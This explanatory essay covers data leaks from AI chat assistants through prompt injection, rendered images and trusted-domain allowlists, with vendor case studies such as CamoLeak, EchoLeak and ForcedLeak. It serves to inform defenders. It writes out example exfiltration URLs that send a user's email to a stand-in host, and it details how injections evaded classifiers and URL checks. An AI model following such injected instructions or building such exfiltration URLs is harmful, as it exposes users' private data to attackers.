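# How AI product teams trade convenience features against the risk of data leaks

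## How a chat assistant can leak data, and what a product team can restrict

A chat assistant, such as ChatGPT, Claude, Gemini or Microsoft Copilot, is a program that answers typed requests using a large language model, a system trained on huge amounts of text to predict what text comes next. For convenience, companies have added features that let an assistant show pictures in its answers, open web pages, offer links, and read a user's email or files through a connector, which connects the assistant to an outside account. An agent uses tools like these to carry out a task over many steps, often while the user does something else.

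Most of these conveniences contact another computer over the internet, and that contact can carry private data. Security researchers use the term data exfiltration, or leak for short, for the unauthorised sending of private data to an outsider. A product team that learns of a leak has to decide how much of the feature behind it to give up. Companies seldom explain these decisions publicly, so people outside the company can often see only the fix.

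### An address carries more than a destination

A web address, or URL, can carry data as well as identify a page. To load a page or a picture, a browser sends the address to the server, the computer that stores it. The address can include extra values after a question mark, which websites often use to pass along a search term or a page number. Websites also commonly record the addresses that visitors request. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that an attacker who gets private data into an address on a site the attacker controls can read that data in the site's log.

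Take a made-up user, Ana, whose email address is ana@mail.example. She asks her assistant to summarise the morning's messages. The assistant writes its answer in Markdown, a plain-text notation that chat interfaces turn into formatted text, links and images. At the end of the answer stands the notation for an image, with this address:

`pictures.example/sun.png?note=ana@mail.example`

The chat page now renders the answer, which means that it turns the assistant's text into what Ana sees. To show the picture, her browser has to fetch it, so it requests that address from pictures.example. The server ignores the note and returns a drawing of a sun. Its log gains a line:

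`09:14 GET /sun.png?note=ana@mail.example`

The owner of pictures.example now has Ana's email address, even though Ana saw only a picture of a sun and didn't click anything. This is a zero-click attack, which needs no action from the victim beyond ordinary use of the assistant.

Marketers used this trick before chat assistants existed, by putting invisible one-pixel images into emails, each with an address unique to the recipient, to see who opened the message. MITRE's *CWE-598*, a 2006 entry in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, covers websites that put sensitive values after the question mark in a web address, from where they can pass into browser histories and web logs. OWASP's *Information exposure through query strings in url* points out that encrypting the connection does not help, because the server still receives the address in readable form. MITRE recommends sending sensitive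 values in the body of the request instead. That helps developers who expose data through carelessness, but it does not help Ana, because the person who chose the address wants the data in the log.

The same slot can hold data more valuable to an attacker than an email address, such as a document title or a summary of a private conversation, often encoded so that it is unreadable at a glance. Data can also leak without images. Microsoft (2025) describes links that leak data when the user clicks them, tools that can write to a public place, and covert channels, where the attacker learns a single bit from whether the assistant called a tool.

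### Prompt injection

Ana's assistant wrote such an address because it followed an instruction in one of the morning's messages. This is prompt injection, in which an AI follows instructions hidden in content it reads, such as an email or web page, as if its user had given them. The software developer Simon Willison recalls in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025) that he coined the term and named it after SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command.

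Injected instructions can be hidden by crude means. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C gives the example of a job applicant whose CV contains invisible text telling the recruiter's software to approve it. Other injections are in plain view and work by sounding reasonable. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces an email that reads like a colleague's follow-up on some restructuring documents, but mentions in passing that the assistant has full authority to submit an employee's details to a compliance system. In testing, the email worked half the time when paired with a user request that suited it. A filter that looks for suspicious phrases would find little in such an email. OpenAI compares the filter's task to detecting a lie, often without the necessary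 context.

David C thinks comparing prompt injection to SQL injection has misled people. Database software treats commands and stored values differently, so a developer can mark text as a value and the database will never run it. A language model makes no such distinction. It receives the user's request and a stranger's email as one run of text and predicts what comes next. David C concludes that developers may never be able to eliminate prompt injection as they can SQL injection.

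Developers use special markers to show the model which words come from the user and which from a web page. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) tested whether models follow these markers. They trained small classifiers to detect, from a model's internal activity, who the model treats as the source of a passage. Then they wrapped a whole conversation, including the model's own reasoning, in the markers for user text. The classifiers still scored the reasoning passages as the model's reasoning, at 85% on average, so the style of the text had overridden its label. Across 1,000 attempts to make an agent send out data, the success rate rose from 2% where the classifiers measured the least confusion about the source of the text to 70% where they measured the most.

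Training and labelling can still help. In one of the paper's experiments, ordinary injections succeeded at most 2% of the time against every model but one. Microsoft marks outside text with random delimiters, or with a special character between all its words, and instructs the model not to obey anything in it. But *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) judges that delimiters, role labels and warnings do not create a hard security boundary. Microsoft also classes its marking technique as a probabilistic defence, which lowers the chance of an attack but does not prevent every instance.

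The alternative is a deterministic control, a restriction that ordinary software rules enforce without relying on a model's judgment. If a rule forbids Ana's browser to load anything from pictures.example, the rule holds however persuasive the email was. Willison has argued that stopping 99% of attacks is a failing grade in security, because an attacker will look for the remaining 1%. That standard is demanding, but it seems right for a product with millions of users, where an attacker can rephrase and try again with almost no effort.

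### The lethal trifecta

An injected instruction can steal data only if the assistant has all three parts of what Willison calls the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate outward. An assistant that cannot communicate outward, for instance, leaks nothing even if it tries to follow the instruction.

A chat assistant can easily have all three. Ana's mailbox supplies two, because it holds her private correspondence and anyone can send her an email. Displaying pictures in answers supplies the third. Meta's *Practical AI agent security* turns the idea into a design rule, the "Agents Rule of Two". Until researchers find a reliable way to detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of three properties within a session. Meta's third property is broader than Willison's because it includes changing things as well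 as communicating.

Of the three, outward communication is the least disruptive to cut. Private data is the whole reason to connect a mailbox. Blocking untrusted content would stop the assistant from reading email from strangers, documents that other people share and most web pages, which is much of what it is for. If the team cuts outward communication instead, the assistant can still read the mailbox and tell Ana what is in it, though she loses a picture of a sun. In June 2026 Willison called outward communication "by far the easiest leg to restrict", meaning that the system stays useful without it. A year earlier he had listed more than a dozen leaks that researchers had reported in commercial products, and noted that the vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by closing the outward route.

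It is documented that the vendors did this, but their reasons are mostly inferred. OpenAI comes close to stating its own. It compares an agent to a customer support worker who can issue refunds. The employer expects some customers to deceive the worker, so it uses software to cap the refunds. Similarly, OpenAI wants to keep the damage from a successful manipulation small and prevent potentially sensitive transmissions from happening silently.

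The trade-off depends on the product, however. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026) argues that a fixed list of permitted domains would severely limit systems that are valuable because they draw on broad outside knowledge. For example, an agent that compares forty hotels needs access to forty hotel websites. Blocking the route by which data leaves also doesn't remove the injection, so a hidden instruction can still distort the summary that Ana reads.

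A less blunt option is to make the restriction depend on what the assistant has just read. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner et al., 2025) proposes that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, the design must make it impossible for that input to trigger any consequential action. David C passes on a similar suggestion, that a model reading someone's text should drop to that person's privileges. Ana's assistant might then browse freely until it opens a stranger's email, but not afterwards. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues acknowledge that their patterns limit an agent's ability to perform arbitrary tasks.

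### Allowlists and Content Security Policy

A team can close the image route in the product's own code or leave the enforcement to the browser. The code can delete the image notation before the page renders the answer, or it can check the image's address against an allowlist of permitted domains or addresses and block everything else.

Websites can use a Content Security Policy (CSP), a rule sent to the browser that limits the domains from which images and other content may load. Suppose the chat page's policy permits images only from the company's own domain. When Ana's browser reaches the image of the sun, it finds that pictures.example is not on the list and never sends the request, so no line appears in the log.

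W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft from the web's main standards body, describes this use and explains that a policy protects only as well as its loosest rule. A policy that forbids everything by default but permits images from anywhere lets data leak through images. W3C recommends CSP as an extra layer against injected content, not as the first line of defence. The browser applies the policy only to what it loads for the page. When an assistant opens a web page, the request may leave from the company's servers, and in that case the team needs separate rules for network egress, the outbound traffic from the environment in which the assistant runs.

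### The possible responses

A team with a leak in front of it has roughly eight choices, and it can combine them.

| Response | What the user loses | Is the control deterministic? |
|---|---|---|
| Remove the feature | The convenience, including every harmless use of it | Yes, for that route |
| Limit it to approved destinations | Everything hosted elsewhere | Yes, but only as sound as the list |
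| Check each request | Some legitimate requests, and some time | Yes if a fixed rule decides, no if a model does |
| Ask the user | Attention, and the ability to leave the agent alone | The pause is; the user's answer is not |
| Turn it off by default | The convenience, until the user finds the setting | Yes while it is off |
| Offer a strict mode | Often several features at once, for those who opt in | Yes inside the mode, if fixed rules enforce it |
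| Warn only | Nothing except the time to read the warning | No; it blocks nothing |
| Accept the risk | No function, but the user carries the exposure | There is no control |

A "yes" in the last column is a limited guarantee. Removing images guarantees that no data leaks through images, but data can still leak through links. An allowlist guarantees only that a request goes first to a listed domain. OpenAI notes that many legitimate sites redirect visitors to other sites. A check of only the first domain will miss these redirects.

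Checking each request aims to restore some of the access that an allowlist blocks. The check can be a fixed rule, like ChatGPT's test of whether the exact address already exists on the public web. It can also be a second model that flags requests that look like leaks, but that defence is probabilistic again, and a clever enough email may mislead the second model too.

An assistant can ask the user before taking a risky action, because she is the one who knows what she wanted. In Outlook, Microsoft's Copilot can draft an email, but the user has to approve and send it. Microsoft concedes that this makes the user experience somewhat worse. Its guidance for developers, *Defend indirect prompt injection*, calls verifying risky actions with the user the last line of defence. Approval protects the user less when she can't see exactly what she is approving. According to *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your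 Data*, current agent frameworks ask for approval of a whole tool, such as web search, and interfaces typically shorten long web addresses. Ana could therefore approve "web search" in good faith and never see the note with her email address in it. Asking more often can also backfire, because OpenAI warns that frequent prompts can train people to click through without thinking.

A product team can impose the same technical restriction by turning a feature off by default or by offering a strict mode. Turning it off by default protects everyone who never changes the settings, while a strict mode such as ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode protects only the people who switch it on.

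A warning takes the company little effort but doesn't block any requests, so it only helps if the reader understands the threat and acts on it. Accepting the risk can be sensible when the data isn't sensitive and the feature is valuable, but outsiders can't distinguish this from never having made a decision. Few product announcements mention the limit David C sets on accepting risk, which is that if a system's security cannot tolerate the risk that remains, the task may not be a good use for a language model.

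## Images in answers: blocked, checked or removed

The first popular chat assistants could leak data through images, as in the example of Ana's email address. In April 2023 the security researcher Johann Rehberger reported the problem to Microsoft and, a day later, to OpenAI, because Bing Chat and ChatGPT both displayed images from any server. Microsoft blocked images from outside its own domains. OpenAI at first declined to change anything, then continued to allow outside images but began checking each one. In 2025 GitHub, a Microsoft subsidiary that hosts software projects, faced a cleverer version of the leak and removed images from its assistant's answers.

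### Bing Chat blocks outside images

Bing Chat, the assistant in Microsoft's search engine, could answer questions about the web page a user had open. Rehberger described his attack on it in *Bing Chat*, a post on his blog Embrace The Red. An attacker could take over the conversation with just a comment or an advertisement on the page. In his demonstration, the assistant carried on normally for two more turns, then wrote an image whose address contained an encoded summary of the page and the chat, including a secret from further down the page. Rehberger added the delay to show how completely an attacker could control the assistant.

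Microsoft notified Rehberger of a fix on 15 June 2023, although he has since dated it to May. His old attacks no longer worked, and the page now had a Content Security Policy that let images load from four Bing hosts. The product still needed those hosts for things such as pictures that Bing Chat generated on request. The policy was the only part of the fix Rehberger could see, so he acknowledged that Microsoft might have changed other things too.

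An advantage of the policy was that researchers could check which domains it permitted, because a website sends its policy to the browser, where anyone can read it. Users also lost little. Pictures could no longer load directly from other people's servers, but Microsoft could still show any picture it hosted itself.

Google made much the same choice for Gemini, but in the product's own code. The security company Checkmarx quotes Google's explanation that a "markdown sanitizer" identifies external image addresses and doesn't render the images. Both approaches depend on the permitted hosts being harmless. EchoLeak, a 2025 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, got data out through a domain that Microsoft trusted.

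### ChatGPT checks each image

OpenAI initially marked Rehberger's report "won't fix", according to Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration Vulnerabilities in LLM apps (Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude)*. SecurityWeek, a trade publication, reported that OpenAI considered the behaviour a feature and did not plan to address it.

That position was easier to defend in the spring of 2023 than at the end of the year. One version of the attack required the victim to copy text from the attacker's website and paste it into the chat, which limited how many people an attacker could reach. But OpenAI kept adding ways for outside text to enter the chat, and Rehberger said that plugins, browsing and custom versions of ChatGPT raised the risk. In December 2023 he demonstrated the attack live, and his server received a consenting victim's conversation. The next day he noticed that OpenAI had begun to check images.

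His post Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes the check, which OpenAI named url_safe. It worked in four steps:

1. The model wrote an answer containing an image, and OpenAI's server sent the answer to the user's browser.
2. Before displaying the image, the code of the ChatGPT web page sent the image's full address to the url_safe service on OpenAI's servers.
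3. The service replied that the address was safe or unsafe.
4. If the address was safe, the browser fetched the image from the outside server. Otherwise the page didn't render it, and no request went to that server.

When Rehberger tried a URL ending in an email address, the service returned "unsafe", so Ana's picture of the sun would have failed too. Users still kept more of the feature than Bing Chat's users did, because images from other domains could appear if they passed the check.

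OpenAI did not publish the rule behind the verdicts. Rehberger guessed that the service might check whether an image was already in Bing's index of the web, and hoped that a language model wasn't making the decision alone. OpenAI did later build a check based on its own index of public addresses. Rehberger soon found a gap in the original rule.

Suppose an attacker's website holds a separate picture for every letter of the alphabet. If an answer displays the picture for "h" and then the picture for "i", the site's log records two requests that together spell "hi". A check of one address at a time will find nothing wrong, because neither address contains private data and the message is conveyed by the choice and order of the pictures.

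In a quick test, Rehberger tried this with a picture address for each of the 26 letters and ten digits, and nine of the 36 passed. He could see no reason why the one for "a" passed and the one for "d" did not. He then sent the word "hi" to an outside server, one letter at a time.

Limiting an attacker to nine distinguishable pictures out of 36 closes less than three-quarters of the leak. The attacker doesn't need a picture for every letter and can rewrite the stolen text in a nine-symbol code, much as Morse code spells every letter with a few signals. Each picture then carries about 3.2 bits of information, compared with 5.2 bits for 36 pictures, so the attacker needs only about 1.6 times as many pictures to send the same text.

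The attack had other practical limits. It was slow, a user might notice a string of odd pictures, and OpenAI could look for the pattern in its own service's records. Browsers also often keep copies of pictures they have fetched, so a repeated letter might never reach the attacker's log, and requests can arrive out of order. Rehberger suggested that OpenAI display only one image per answer, or a handful at most. This rule would have been crude, but unlike the check, it would have limited the number of requests.

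Willison (2023) called url_safe a "half-baked solution" and found it odd that OpenAI hadn't blocked images from external domains. That criticism seems fair for the 2023 version. The check was an improvement because it stopped an attacker from taking a whole summary of a conversation in one request. But even a few leaked characters can matter if they belong to a password, and Rehberger kept finding ways around the check. He presented some of them at the Black Hat Europe security conference in 2024. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, he dates the changes that stopped those attacks to around August 2025, about 20 months after the launch.

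### Web fixes that missed the phone

The second gap in url_safe was that it checked an image only if the app displaying the answer called it. The service ran on OpenAI's servers, but the call had to come from the web page's code. ChatGPT's iPhone app has its own code for displaying answers, and the version Rehberger examined in December 2023 never made the call. It fetched every image unchecked, so the original attack still worked. He thought the Android app probably had the same problem.

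A Content Security Policy can leave the same gap, because it doesn't protect answers that a phone app displays with its own code.

Rehberger argued on Embrace The Red that OpenAI should check images on its servers, where one fix would protect every app. He suspected that OpenAI had put the check in the web page for speed. ChatGPT sends an answer piece by piece while the model is still writing, so OpenAI would have to hold back the part with the image until a server check finished. Covering all the apps at once seems worth a short pause before a picture appears, though OpenAI has not published how it weighed the two.

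The gap lasted beyond the first weeks. In 2026, Rehberger recalled that OpenAI's macOS and iOS apps had both lacked the check. He warned that OpenAI could still have the same trouble with its newer protections, because a developer building a new feature may not know about them. He had often seen this in security work.

In July 2023 Rehberger showed that instructions in an uploaded file could also make Anthropic's Claude write a Markdown image that sent out the chat history when it loaded. Anthropic closed the case two weeks later, as he reports in Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*. After the fix, Claude loaded a Markdown image only when the user clicked "Show Image", so users could still see images but no data was sent automatically. Rehberger considered the fix imperfect. Like other approval prompts, it is weak because a user who expects a picture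 will probably click.

In December 2024, 17 months later, Rehberger announced that Anthropic had fixed a leak through images in Claude's iPhone app. In the announcement, quoted by Willison (2024), he remarked that mobile apps often have this kind of leak too. He didn't explain whether the phone app had ever had the "Show Image" button. Either way, people who used Claude on both a computer and a phone had been less safe on the phone, and probably couldn't have known it.

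### Smaller fixes

Other teams found easier or narrower fixes. Azure AI Playground was a Microsoft website where developers could try out models. It could not pull in outside content by itself, so a victim had to paste in the malicious text, and Rehberger rated the problem as medium. Microsoft finished its fix in September 2023. According to Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground*, the fix appeared from the outside to insert a space into the notation for an image, so that the page displayed it as ordinary text. This removes images as effectively as any other method, but only while the page keeps reading the notation in the same way.

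The version of Copilot Chat in Microsoft's code editor, VS Code, had the problem, and an attacker could plant the instructions in a source code comment. Rehberger reported this in February 2024 and received confirmation of a fix in June. Microsoft explained the fix so little that two experienced observers described it differently. Rehberger concluded in Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat* that the assistant no longer rendered Markdown images at all, while Willison described a block on images from untrusted domains. Under Willison's account, the fix was an allowlist, so users could still see images from trusted domains.

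Amp, a coding agent from Sourcegraph, had the same flaw a year later. An attacker could make the agent open a file of passwords and keys on the developer's computer, then leak the contents through an image. According to Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Amp Code*, Sourcegraph fixed the flaw promptly after a report in June 2025, but Rehberger doesn't describe the fix.

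GitLab, a competitor of GitHub, passed each answer from its Duo assistant through DOMPurify, a widely used program that strips dangerous code from web content. DOMPurify is good at removing code that would run in the user's browser, but by default it leaves image tags in place because pictures on an ordinary website are usually harmless. In *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft*, researchers at the security company Legit Security explain how they used such a tag to extract private source code. They reported the flaw in February 2025. GitLab's patch stops Duo from rendering images and web forms that point outside gitlab.com.

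GitLab adopted roughly the same rule that Microsoft had given Bing Chat. GitHub already had a similar rule when Legit Security began investigating the company a few months later.

### CamoLeak: how signed images leaked private code

Copilot Chat on github.com answers questions about software projects. For example, a developer might ask it to explain a pull request, which is a proposed change to a project's code. In June 2025 Omer Mayraz of Legit Security found that he could put instructions for Copilot in the description of a pull request and hide them from human readers. GitHub lets people write comments that the page doesn't display, and Copilot read those too.

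The instructions affected anyone who opened that page and used Copilot there. Copilot had the same permissions as the person using it, so it could read that person's private projects. Mayraz could now use untrusted content to reach private data, and lacked only a way to send that data out.

GitHub's Content Security Policy would have blocked an image like Ana's, because it blocks images from any domain that GitHub doesn't own. But developers often put diagrams and logos hosted elsewhere in a project's README, the file that introduces the project. GitHub displays these through an image proxy called Camo, a server that fetches pictures on the browser's behalf.

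Legit Security's *CamoLeak* explains how GitHub uses Camo, its image proxy. When a developer saves a README, GitHub replaces each outside image's address with a Camo address that includes a signature, a code that GitHub computes with a secret key. When someone views the page, the browser requests the image from Camo, which checks the signature. If the signature matches, Camo fetches the image from its original server and passes it on. Otherwise, Camo fetches nothing.

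GitHub built its image proxy to avoid browser warnings about insecure content, keep visitors' browser details from outside servers and load pages faster, according to its post *Proxying User Images* (2014). The signature on each image address also seemed to rule out the basic image leak, in which a hijacked assistant writes an address that ends in a stolen password. The assistant doesn't have GitHub's key, so it can't produce the matching signature.

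Mayraz got around this by collecting signatures in advance. GitHub will sign an image address for anyone who submits it, since that is how pictures get into READMEs. He got a signed address for each letter and symbol he might need and included them all in his hidden instructions. Copilot then only had to output the addresses in the order that spelled the private text. Each address had a valid signature, so Camo requested the pictures from Mayraz's server, whose log recorded the message. Each picture was a single transparent pixel, so the user saw nothing unusual.

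Mayraz's method uses the same idea as Rehberger's 2023 method, which used pictures of letters, but it worked much better. url_safe had rejected 27 of Rehberger's 36 addresses, while Camo accepted all of Mayraz's. Mayraz also found a way to make Camo fetch a picture again when a letter was repeated, instead of using a stored copy.

A valid signature proves that GitHub generated an image's address, but it doesn't show who is displaying the image or why. GitHub warns in its documentation that anyone who receives one of these addresses can view the image. That is reasonable for a logo in a README, where a person chose the images beforehand and every visitor's browser requests the same ones. In Copilot's answers, however, an attacker could make the choice of images depend on private data.

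In his demonstrations, Mayraz extracted the description of an unfixed security flaw from a private project. He also had Copilot search a victim's code for keys to Amazon's cloud service and send out what it found. Legit Security rates the vulnerability 9.6 out of 10 on CVSS, the standard severity scale. The press reported it in October 2025, after the fix. OECD's *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and Secrets* (2025), an entry in a public database of AI incidents, includes an AI-generated summary that classifies it as an incident rather than a hazard. However, the evidence mentioned in the summary consists of proof-of-concept attacks like Mayraz's.

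### Why GitHub removed images

GitHub told Mayraz on 14 August 2025 that it had fixed the problem. According to Legit Security, GitHub did so by disabling images in Copilot Chat completely. SecurityWeek's *GitHub Copilot Chat Flaw Leaked Data From Private Repositories* paraphrases GitHub's message more narrowly, as a ban on using Camo to leak sensitive information. The two descriptions differ for images that GitHub hosts itself, but they mean nearly the same thing for outside images, because the Content Security Policy already blocked every route except Camo.

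Neither account gives GitHub's reasons, but the alternatives seem to have had drawbacks. GitHub could have blocked the addresses that Mayraz used, but an attacker could have had a new set signed in minutes. Limiting the number of images per answer would have slowed the leak without ending it. Rehberger noted, when discussing ChatGPT, that an attacker could prepare thousands of addresses instead of 36. Each image could then stand for a whole word.

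GitHub could have made a more thorough repair by having Camo fetch each picture once, at signing, and serve only that copy afterwards. Displaying a picture would then send no request to the outside server, and Copilot could have kept its images. But all of GitHub relies on Camo, and some pictures are supposed to change, such as the badges that show whether a project's latest tests passed. GitHub would have had to alter a service that was working well everywhere else to keep a minor feature of one product.

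Removing images from the chat avoided these problems. It required a change in one place, did not depend on predicting how an attacker would encode the data, and left images in READMEs unaffected. It was probably the simplest way to stop leaks through images completely and quickly.

Removing images stopped leaks through images, but it did not affect two other attacks by Mayraz, who had also made Copilot write links that contained private data and recommend a malicious software package. GitHub's current rules for paying outside researchers suggest that, like OpenAI, it concentrates on what a successful injection can achieve. GitHub does not reward reports that show only that hidden text can influence Copilot, but it may reward those that show data crossing from one project to another.

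GitHub kept some images when it fixed another Copilot leak. According to Vulners' *GitHub*, a copy of the company's summary of that leak, the fix allowed images from trusted domains and added warnings about links.

### What users lost, and whether images have returned

The removal went against GitHub's direction for the product. In the month Mayraz found the flaw, GitHub's *Improved attachments and larger context in Copilot Chat in public preview* (2025) announced that users could attach up to four images to a question and preview web pages that included outside pictures.

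Copilot users can still attach their own images and PDFs to questions on github.com, in VS Code and in the command-line version, according to GitHub's *Copilot vision is generally available* (2026). An attached screenshot might contain hidden instructions, but sending it to Copilot doesn't make the browser contact a stranger's server.

Users lost pictures in the answers. If a developer asks how a project fits together, Copilot can explain it in words and link to the diagram in the README, but it can't show the diagram itself. That seems a small loss for an assistant whose answers are mostly code and text, but it would be a larger one in a general assistant that people ask about birds or furniture.

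There is no clear public sign that Copilot Chat on github.com shows outside images again. GitHub's *Application card*, which describes the assistant, lists syntax highlighting, indentation and links among the features of an answer but doesn't mention images.

Microsoft has brought images back elsewhere, in a more limited form. Collab365 Spaces' *Microsoft Copilot now shows images from your files and meetings* (2026) reports that in the second half of July 2026 Microsoft 365 Copilot began showing charts, slides and other visuals from a user's files and meetings in its answers. Previously, users had to open the original file to see them. If these images load from Microsoft's storage, as seems likely, displaying one sends nothing to an outsider, even if its source file contains a prompt injection.

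## Lists of trusted domains and how they failed

GitHub could remove images from Copilot Chat without losing much because most of the assistant's answers are text and code. An allowlist appeals to teams that want to keep images. A company's icons, charts and profile photos usually load from a few of its own domains, so if the assistant's page accepts images only from those domains, users still see nearly everything they saw before. Some companies also remove links that lead outside those domains.

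A list of trusted domains prevents leaks only if attackers can't get the data sent to those domains. Between January 2025 and December 2026, researchers got around this protection in products from Microsoft, Salesforce and the email company Superhuman.

### EchoLeak: a trusted server that fetched other addresses

Microsoft 365 Copilot, the version of Copilot that companies buy for their staff, answers a question by searching the employee's mailbox, files, internal sites and Teams chats and adding whatever seems relevant to the text that the model reads. In January 2025 Aim Labs, the research department of the security company Aim Security, told Microsoft that an outsider could steal data from that text by sending the employee an email, even if the employee never opened it. Aim called the attack EchoLeak. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) explains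 how it got past Microsoft's defences one by one.

Microsoft used classifiers, models trained to recognise prompt injections, to keep malicious text away from Copilot. The classifiers missed Aim's email, which was written as if its instructions were for the recipient and never mentioned an AI. The email also had to turn up in Copilot's searches, so Aim made it long and split it into sections with ordinary office headings, such as staff onboarding and leave of absence. Questions on many subjects would then bring up some part of it.

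Copilot also removed links and images that pointed outside the company. In Markdown, an author can put the address straight after the link's text, or put a label there and give the address further down, like a footnote. Microsoft's filter recognised only the first form, but the chat page rendered both. A filter that checked the finished page instead of the Markdown would have found the outside address in either case.

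The last obstacle was the Content Security Policy. Ravia reproduces the list of domains from which Copilot's page could load images. It has 29 different entries, compared with four for Bing Chat in 2023, and 14 of them appear twice. Many of the names suggest a purpose, such as loading connector icons, LinkedIn photos or pictures from Microsoft's Designer tool. One entry is a storage server on a domain of the US intelligence agencies, which the staff of an ordinary company would presumably never need. Several teams seem to have added domains to the list, and nobody seems to have removed the unneeded ones.

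Eleven of the entries start with a wildcard, which covers every address under a domain. One covers SharePoint, Microsoft's service for internal websites and shared files, which gives each customer an address ending in sharepoint.com. An attacker can become a customer too, so the policy permitted images from the attacker's SharePoint site.

That alone didn't give Aim the data, because SharePoint customers can't run their own code on Microsoft's servers or freely read the servers' logs. Aim needed a page on a listed domain that would pass the data on. An open redirect, an address on a trusted site that forwards the visitor to any other site named in the address, would not have been enough, because the browser also checks the new destination against the policy and would have blocked the request.

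Aim looked instead for a server that fetches other addresses itself. Suppose Ana's company permits images from office.example, and that site has a service for fetching pictures. The hijacked assistant writes an image with this address:

`office.example/fetch?url=pictures.example/sun.png?note=ana@mail.example`

Ana's browser finds office.example on the list and sends the request. The server at office.example then reads the second address and requests the picture from pictures.example, which logs Ana's email address as before. The policy restricts only Ana's browser, so it has no effect on a request between two servers.

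Aim first found such a service in SharePoint, but an attacker could use it only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. The researchers then found another in Teams, Microsoft's chat and meeting product, which needed no invitation. Such services have ordinary uses, like preparing a preview when someone pastes a link into a chat.

The attack could take any text that Copilot had gathered for the model, including the chat history and passages from internal files. *EchoLeak*, an academic case study by Reddy and Gujral, stresses that the attacker could do this remotely and without logging in. According to SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration*, the flaw scored 9.3 out of 10 for severity, and Microsoft said nobody had exploited it.

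Microsoft finished its patch in May 2025, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*, and customers had nothing to install. Before then, they could not protect themselves, because according to Ravia no administrator setting would have stopped the attack. The fix probably took away little functionality, since Copilot was already supposed to remove external links and recognising the second notation only enforced that restriction. Restricting the service in Teams could have been more disruptive if other features relied on it.

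Ravia thinks the underlying fault is what Aim calls an "LLM scope violation", in which text from outside an organisation directs the model to data from inside it. Aim was selling protection against this, so it had a commercial reason to name the problem. But David C's suggestion about dropping a model's privileges rests on a similar principle. The difficulty is that employees want the model to combine outside text with internal data. To answer a client's email with last quarter's figures, for example, Copilot needs to read both the email and the company's files.

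### ForcedLeak: a trusted domain that anyone could register

Companies use Salesforce's software to keep records of their customers, and its Agentforce product lets them build agents that work with those records. Salesforce's Web-to-Lead feature puts a form on a company's website and saves each visitor's entry as a lead (a possible customer). Text from strangers therefore enters the same system as the company's private sales records.

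In 2025 the security company Noma Security used the form to plant instructions in an attack it named ForcedLeak. When an employee asked Agentforce about the new lead, the agent also followed the planted instructions. One was to answer what colour red and yellow make, which a sales agent has no reason to do. Another was to retrieve the email addresses of the company's leads, which the agent then put into the URL of an image presented as a customer's logo. Noma partly blames "overly permissive AI model behavior" in a statement quoted by The Hacker News (2025).

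Salesforce's Content Security Policy should have stopped the image from loading, but it permitted every address under my-salesforce-cms.com. Salesforce had let that domain's registration expire without removing it from the policy (Willison, 2025). Noma registered the domain and received the data there.

This attack needed only a lapsed domain that was still on the trusted list, not clever use of a Microsoft or Google service. A company loses a domain name if it stops renewing the registration, but the policy entry remains until someone deletes it. The browser compares names and doesn't check who owns them. The mistake was dangerous because lapsed domains are easy to find and cheap to register, but a routine check of the list against the company's registrations would have caught it. Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed* reports a severity score of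 9.4.

Salesforce took back control of the domain, which closed the route that Noma had used. It also began enforcing a list called Trusted URLs for the output of Agentforce and its Einstein AI agents. An administrator at each customer company approves outside addresses for the list, and the agents can't send output to any others. The list limits where the agents' output can go in general, so it is broader than a rule about images.

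Under the rule, customers have to keep their lists of trusted domains up to date. For example, if a shop's agent gives buyers a link to a courier's tracking page, an administrator has to approve the courier's domain first, and the link may stop working if the courier moves to a new one. A domain that an administrator approves today can also expire in three years, which would leave the company with a smaller version of Salesforce's problem. Nudge Security's *ForcedLeak indirect prompt injection in Salesforce Agentforce* (2025) advised customers to harden their own systems even after Salesforce's fix. The rule still seems worth the upkeep for agents that read strangers' messages alongside customer records, because most business agents need only a few outside sites and the people who run them know which ones.

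### Superhuman: a trusted site that stored the data

Superhuman makes an email program with an AI assistant. The program's Content Security Policy allowed images from docs.google.com, which hosts Google's online documents. The domain had not expired, and the attack didn't need Google to forward anything.

The same domain also hosts Google Forms, which anyone can use to make a questionnaire and collect the answers. A form accepts answers through its web address, so people can send out links with some fields already filled in. By convention, loading a web address should only retrieve information, not change the server's records. But Willison (2026) points out in *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* that Google Forms saves data sent this way.

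PromptArmor, the security company that found the flaw, made a Google Form and sent the victim an email with hidden instructions. These told the assistant to fill in the form, on the pretext that users must have the option to send feedback on their search results. When the victim asked for a summary of recent mail, the assistant put the contents of other emails into the form's address and used that address as the source of an image. When the browser tried to load the image, Google recorded the emails as a response to the form, where PromptArmor could read them. A single request for a summary exposed dozens of messages, including financial, legal and medical ones.

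A team can check its trusted domains for forwarding pages and still miss this kind of leak. In EchoLeak, the data went on to an unknown server, and Microsoft could in principle have noticed the traffic. In Superhuman's case, the data went no further than Google, and the attacker could read it only because Google gives every form's owner the submitted responses.

Willison credits Superhuman with making the report a high priority and fixing the flaw. The simplest fix would have been to remove docs.google.com from the list of allowed image sources. Users would have lost images that load directly from that domain, but links to Google documents would have kept working, because a rule about images doesn't affect links. That is a small loss in an email program, where most people open documents in a separate window anyway.

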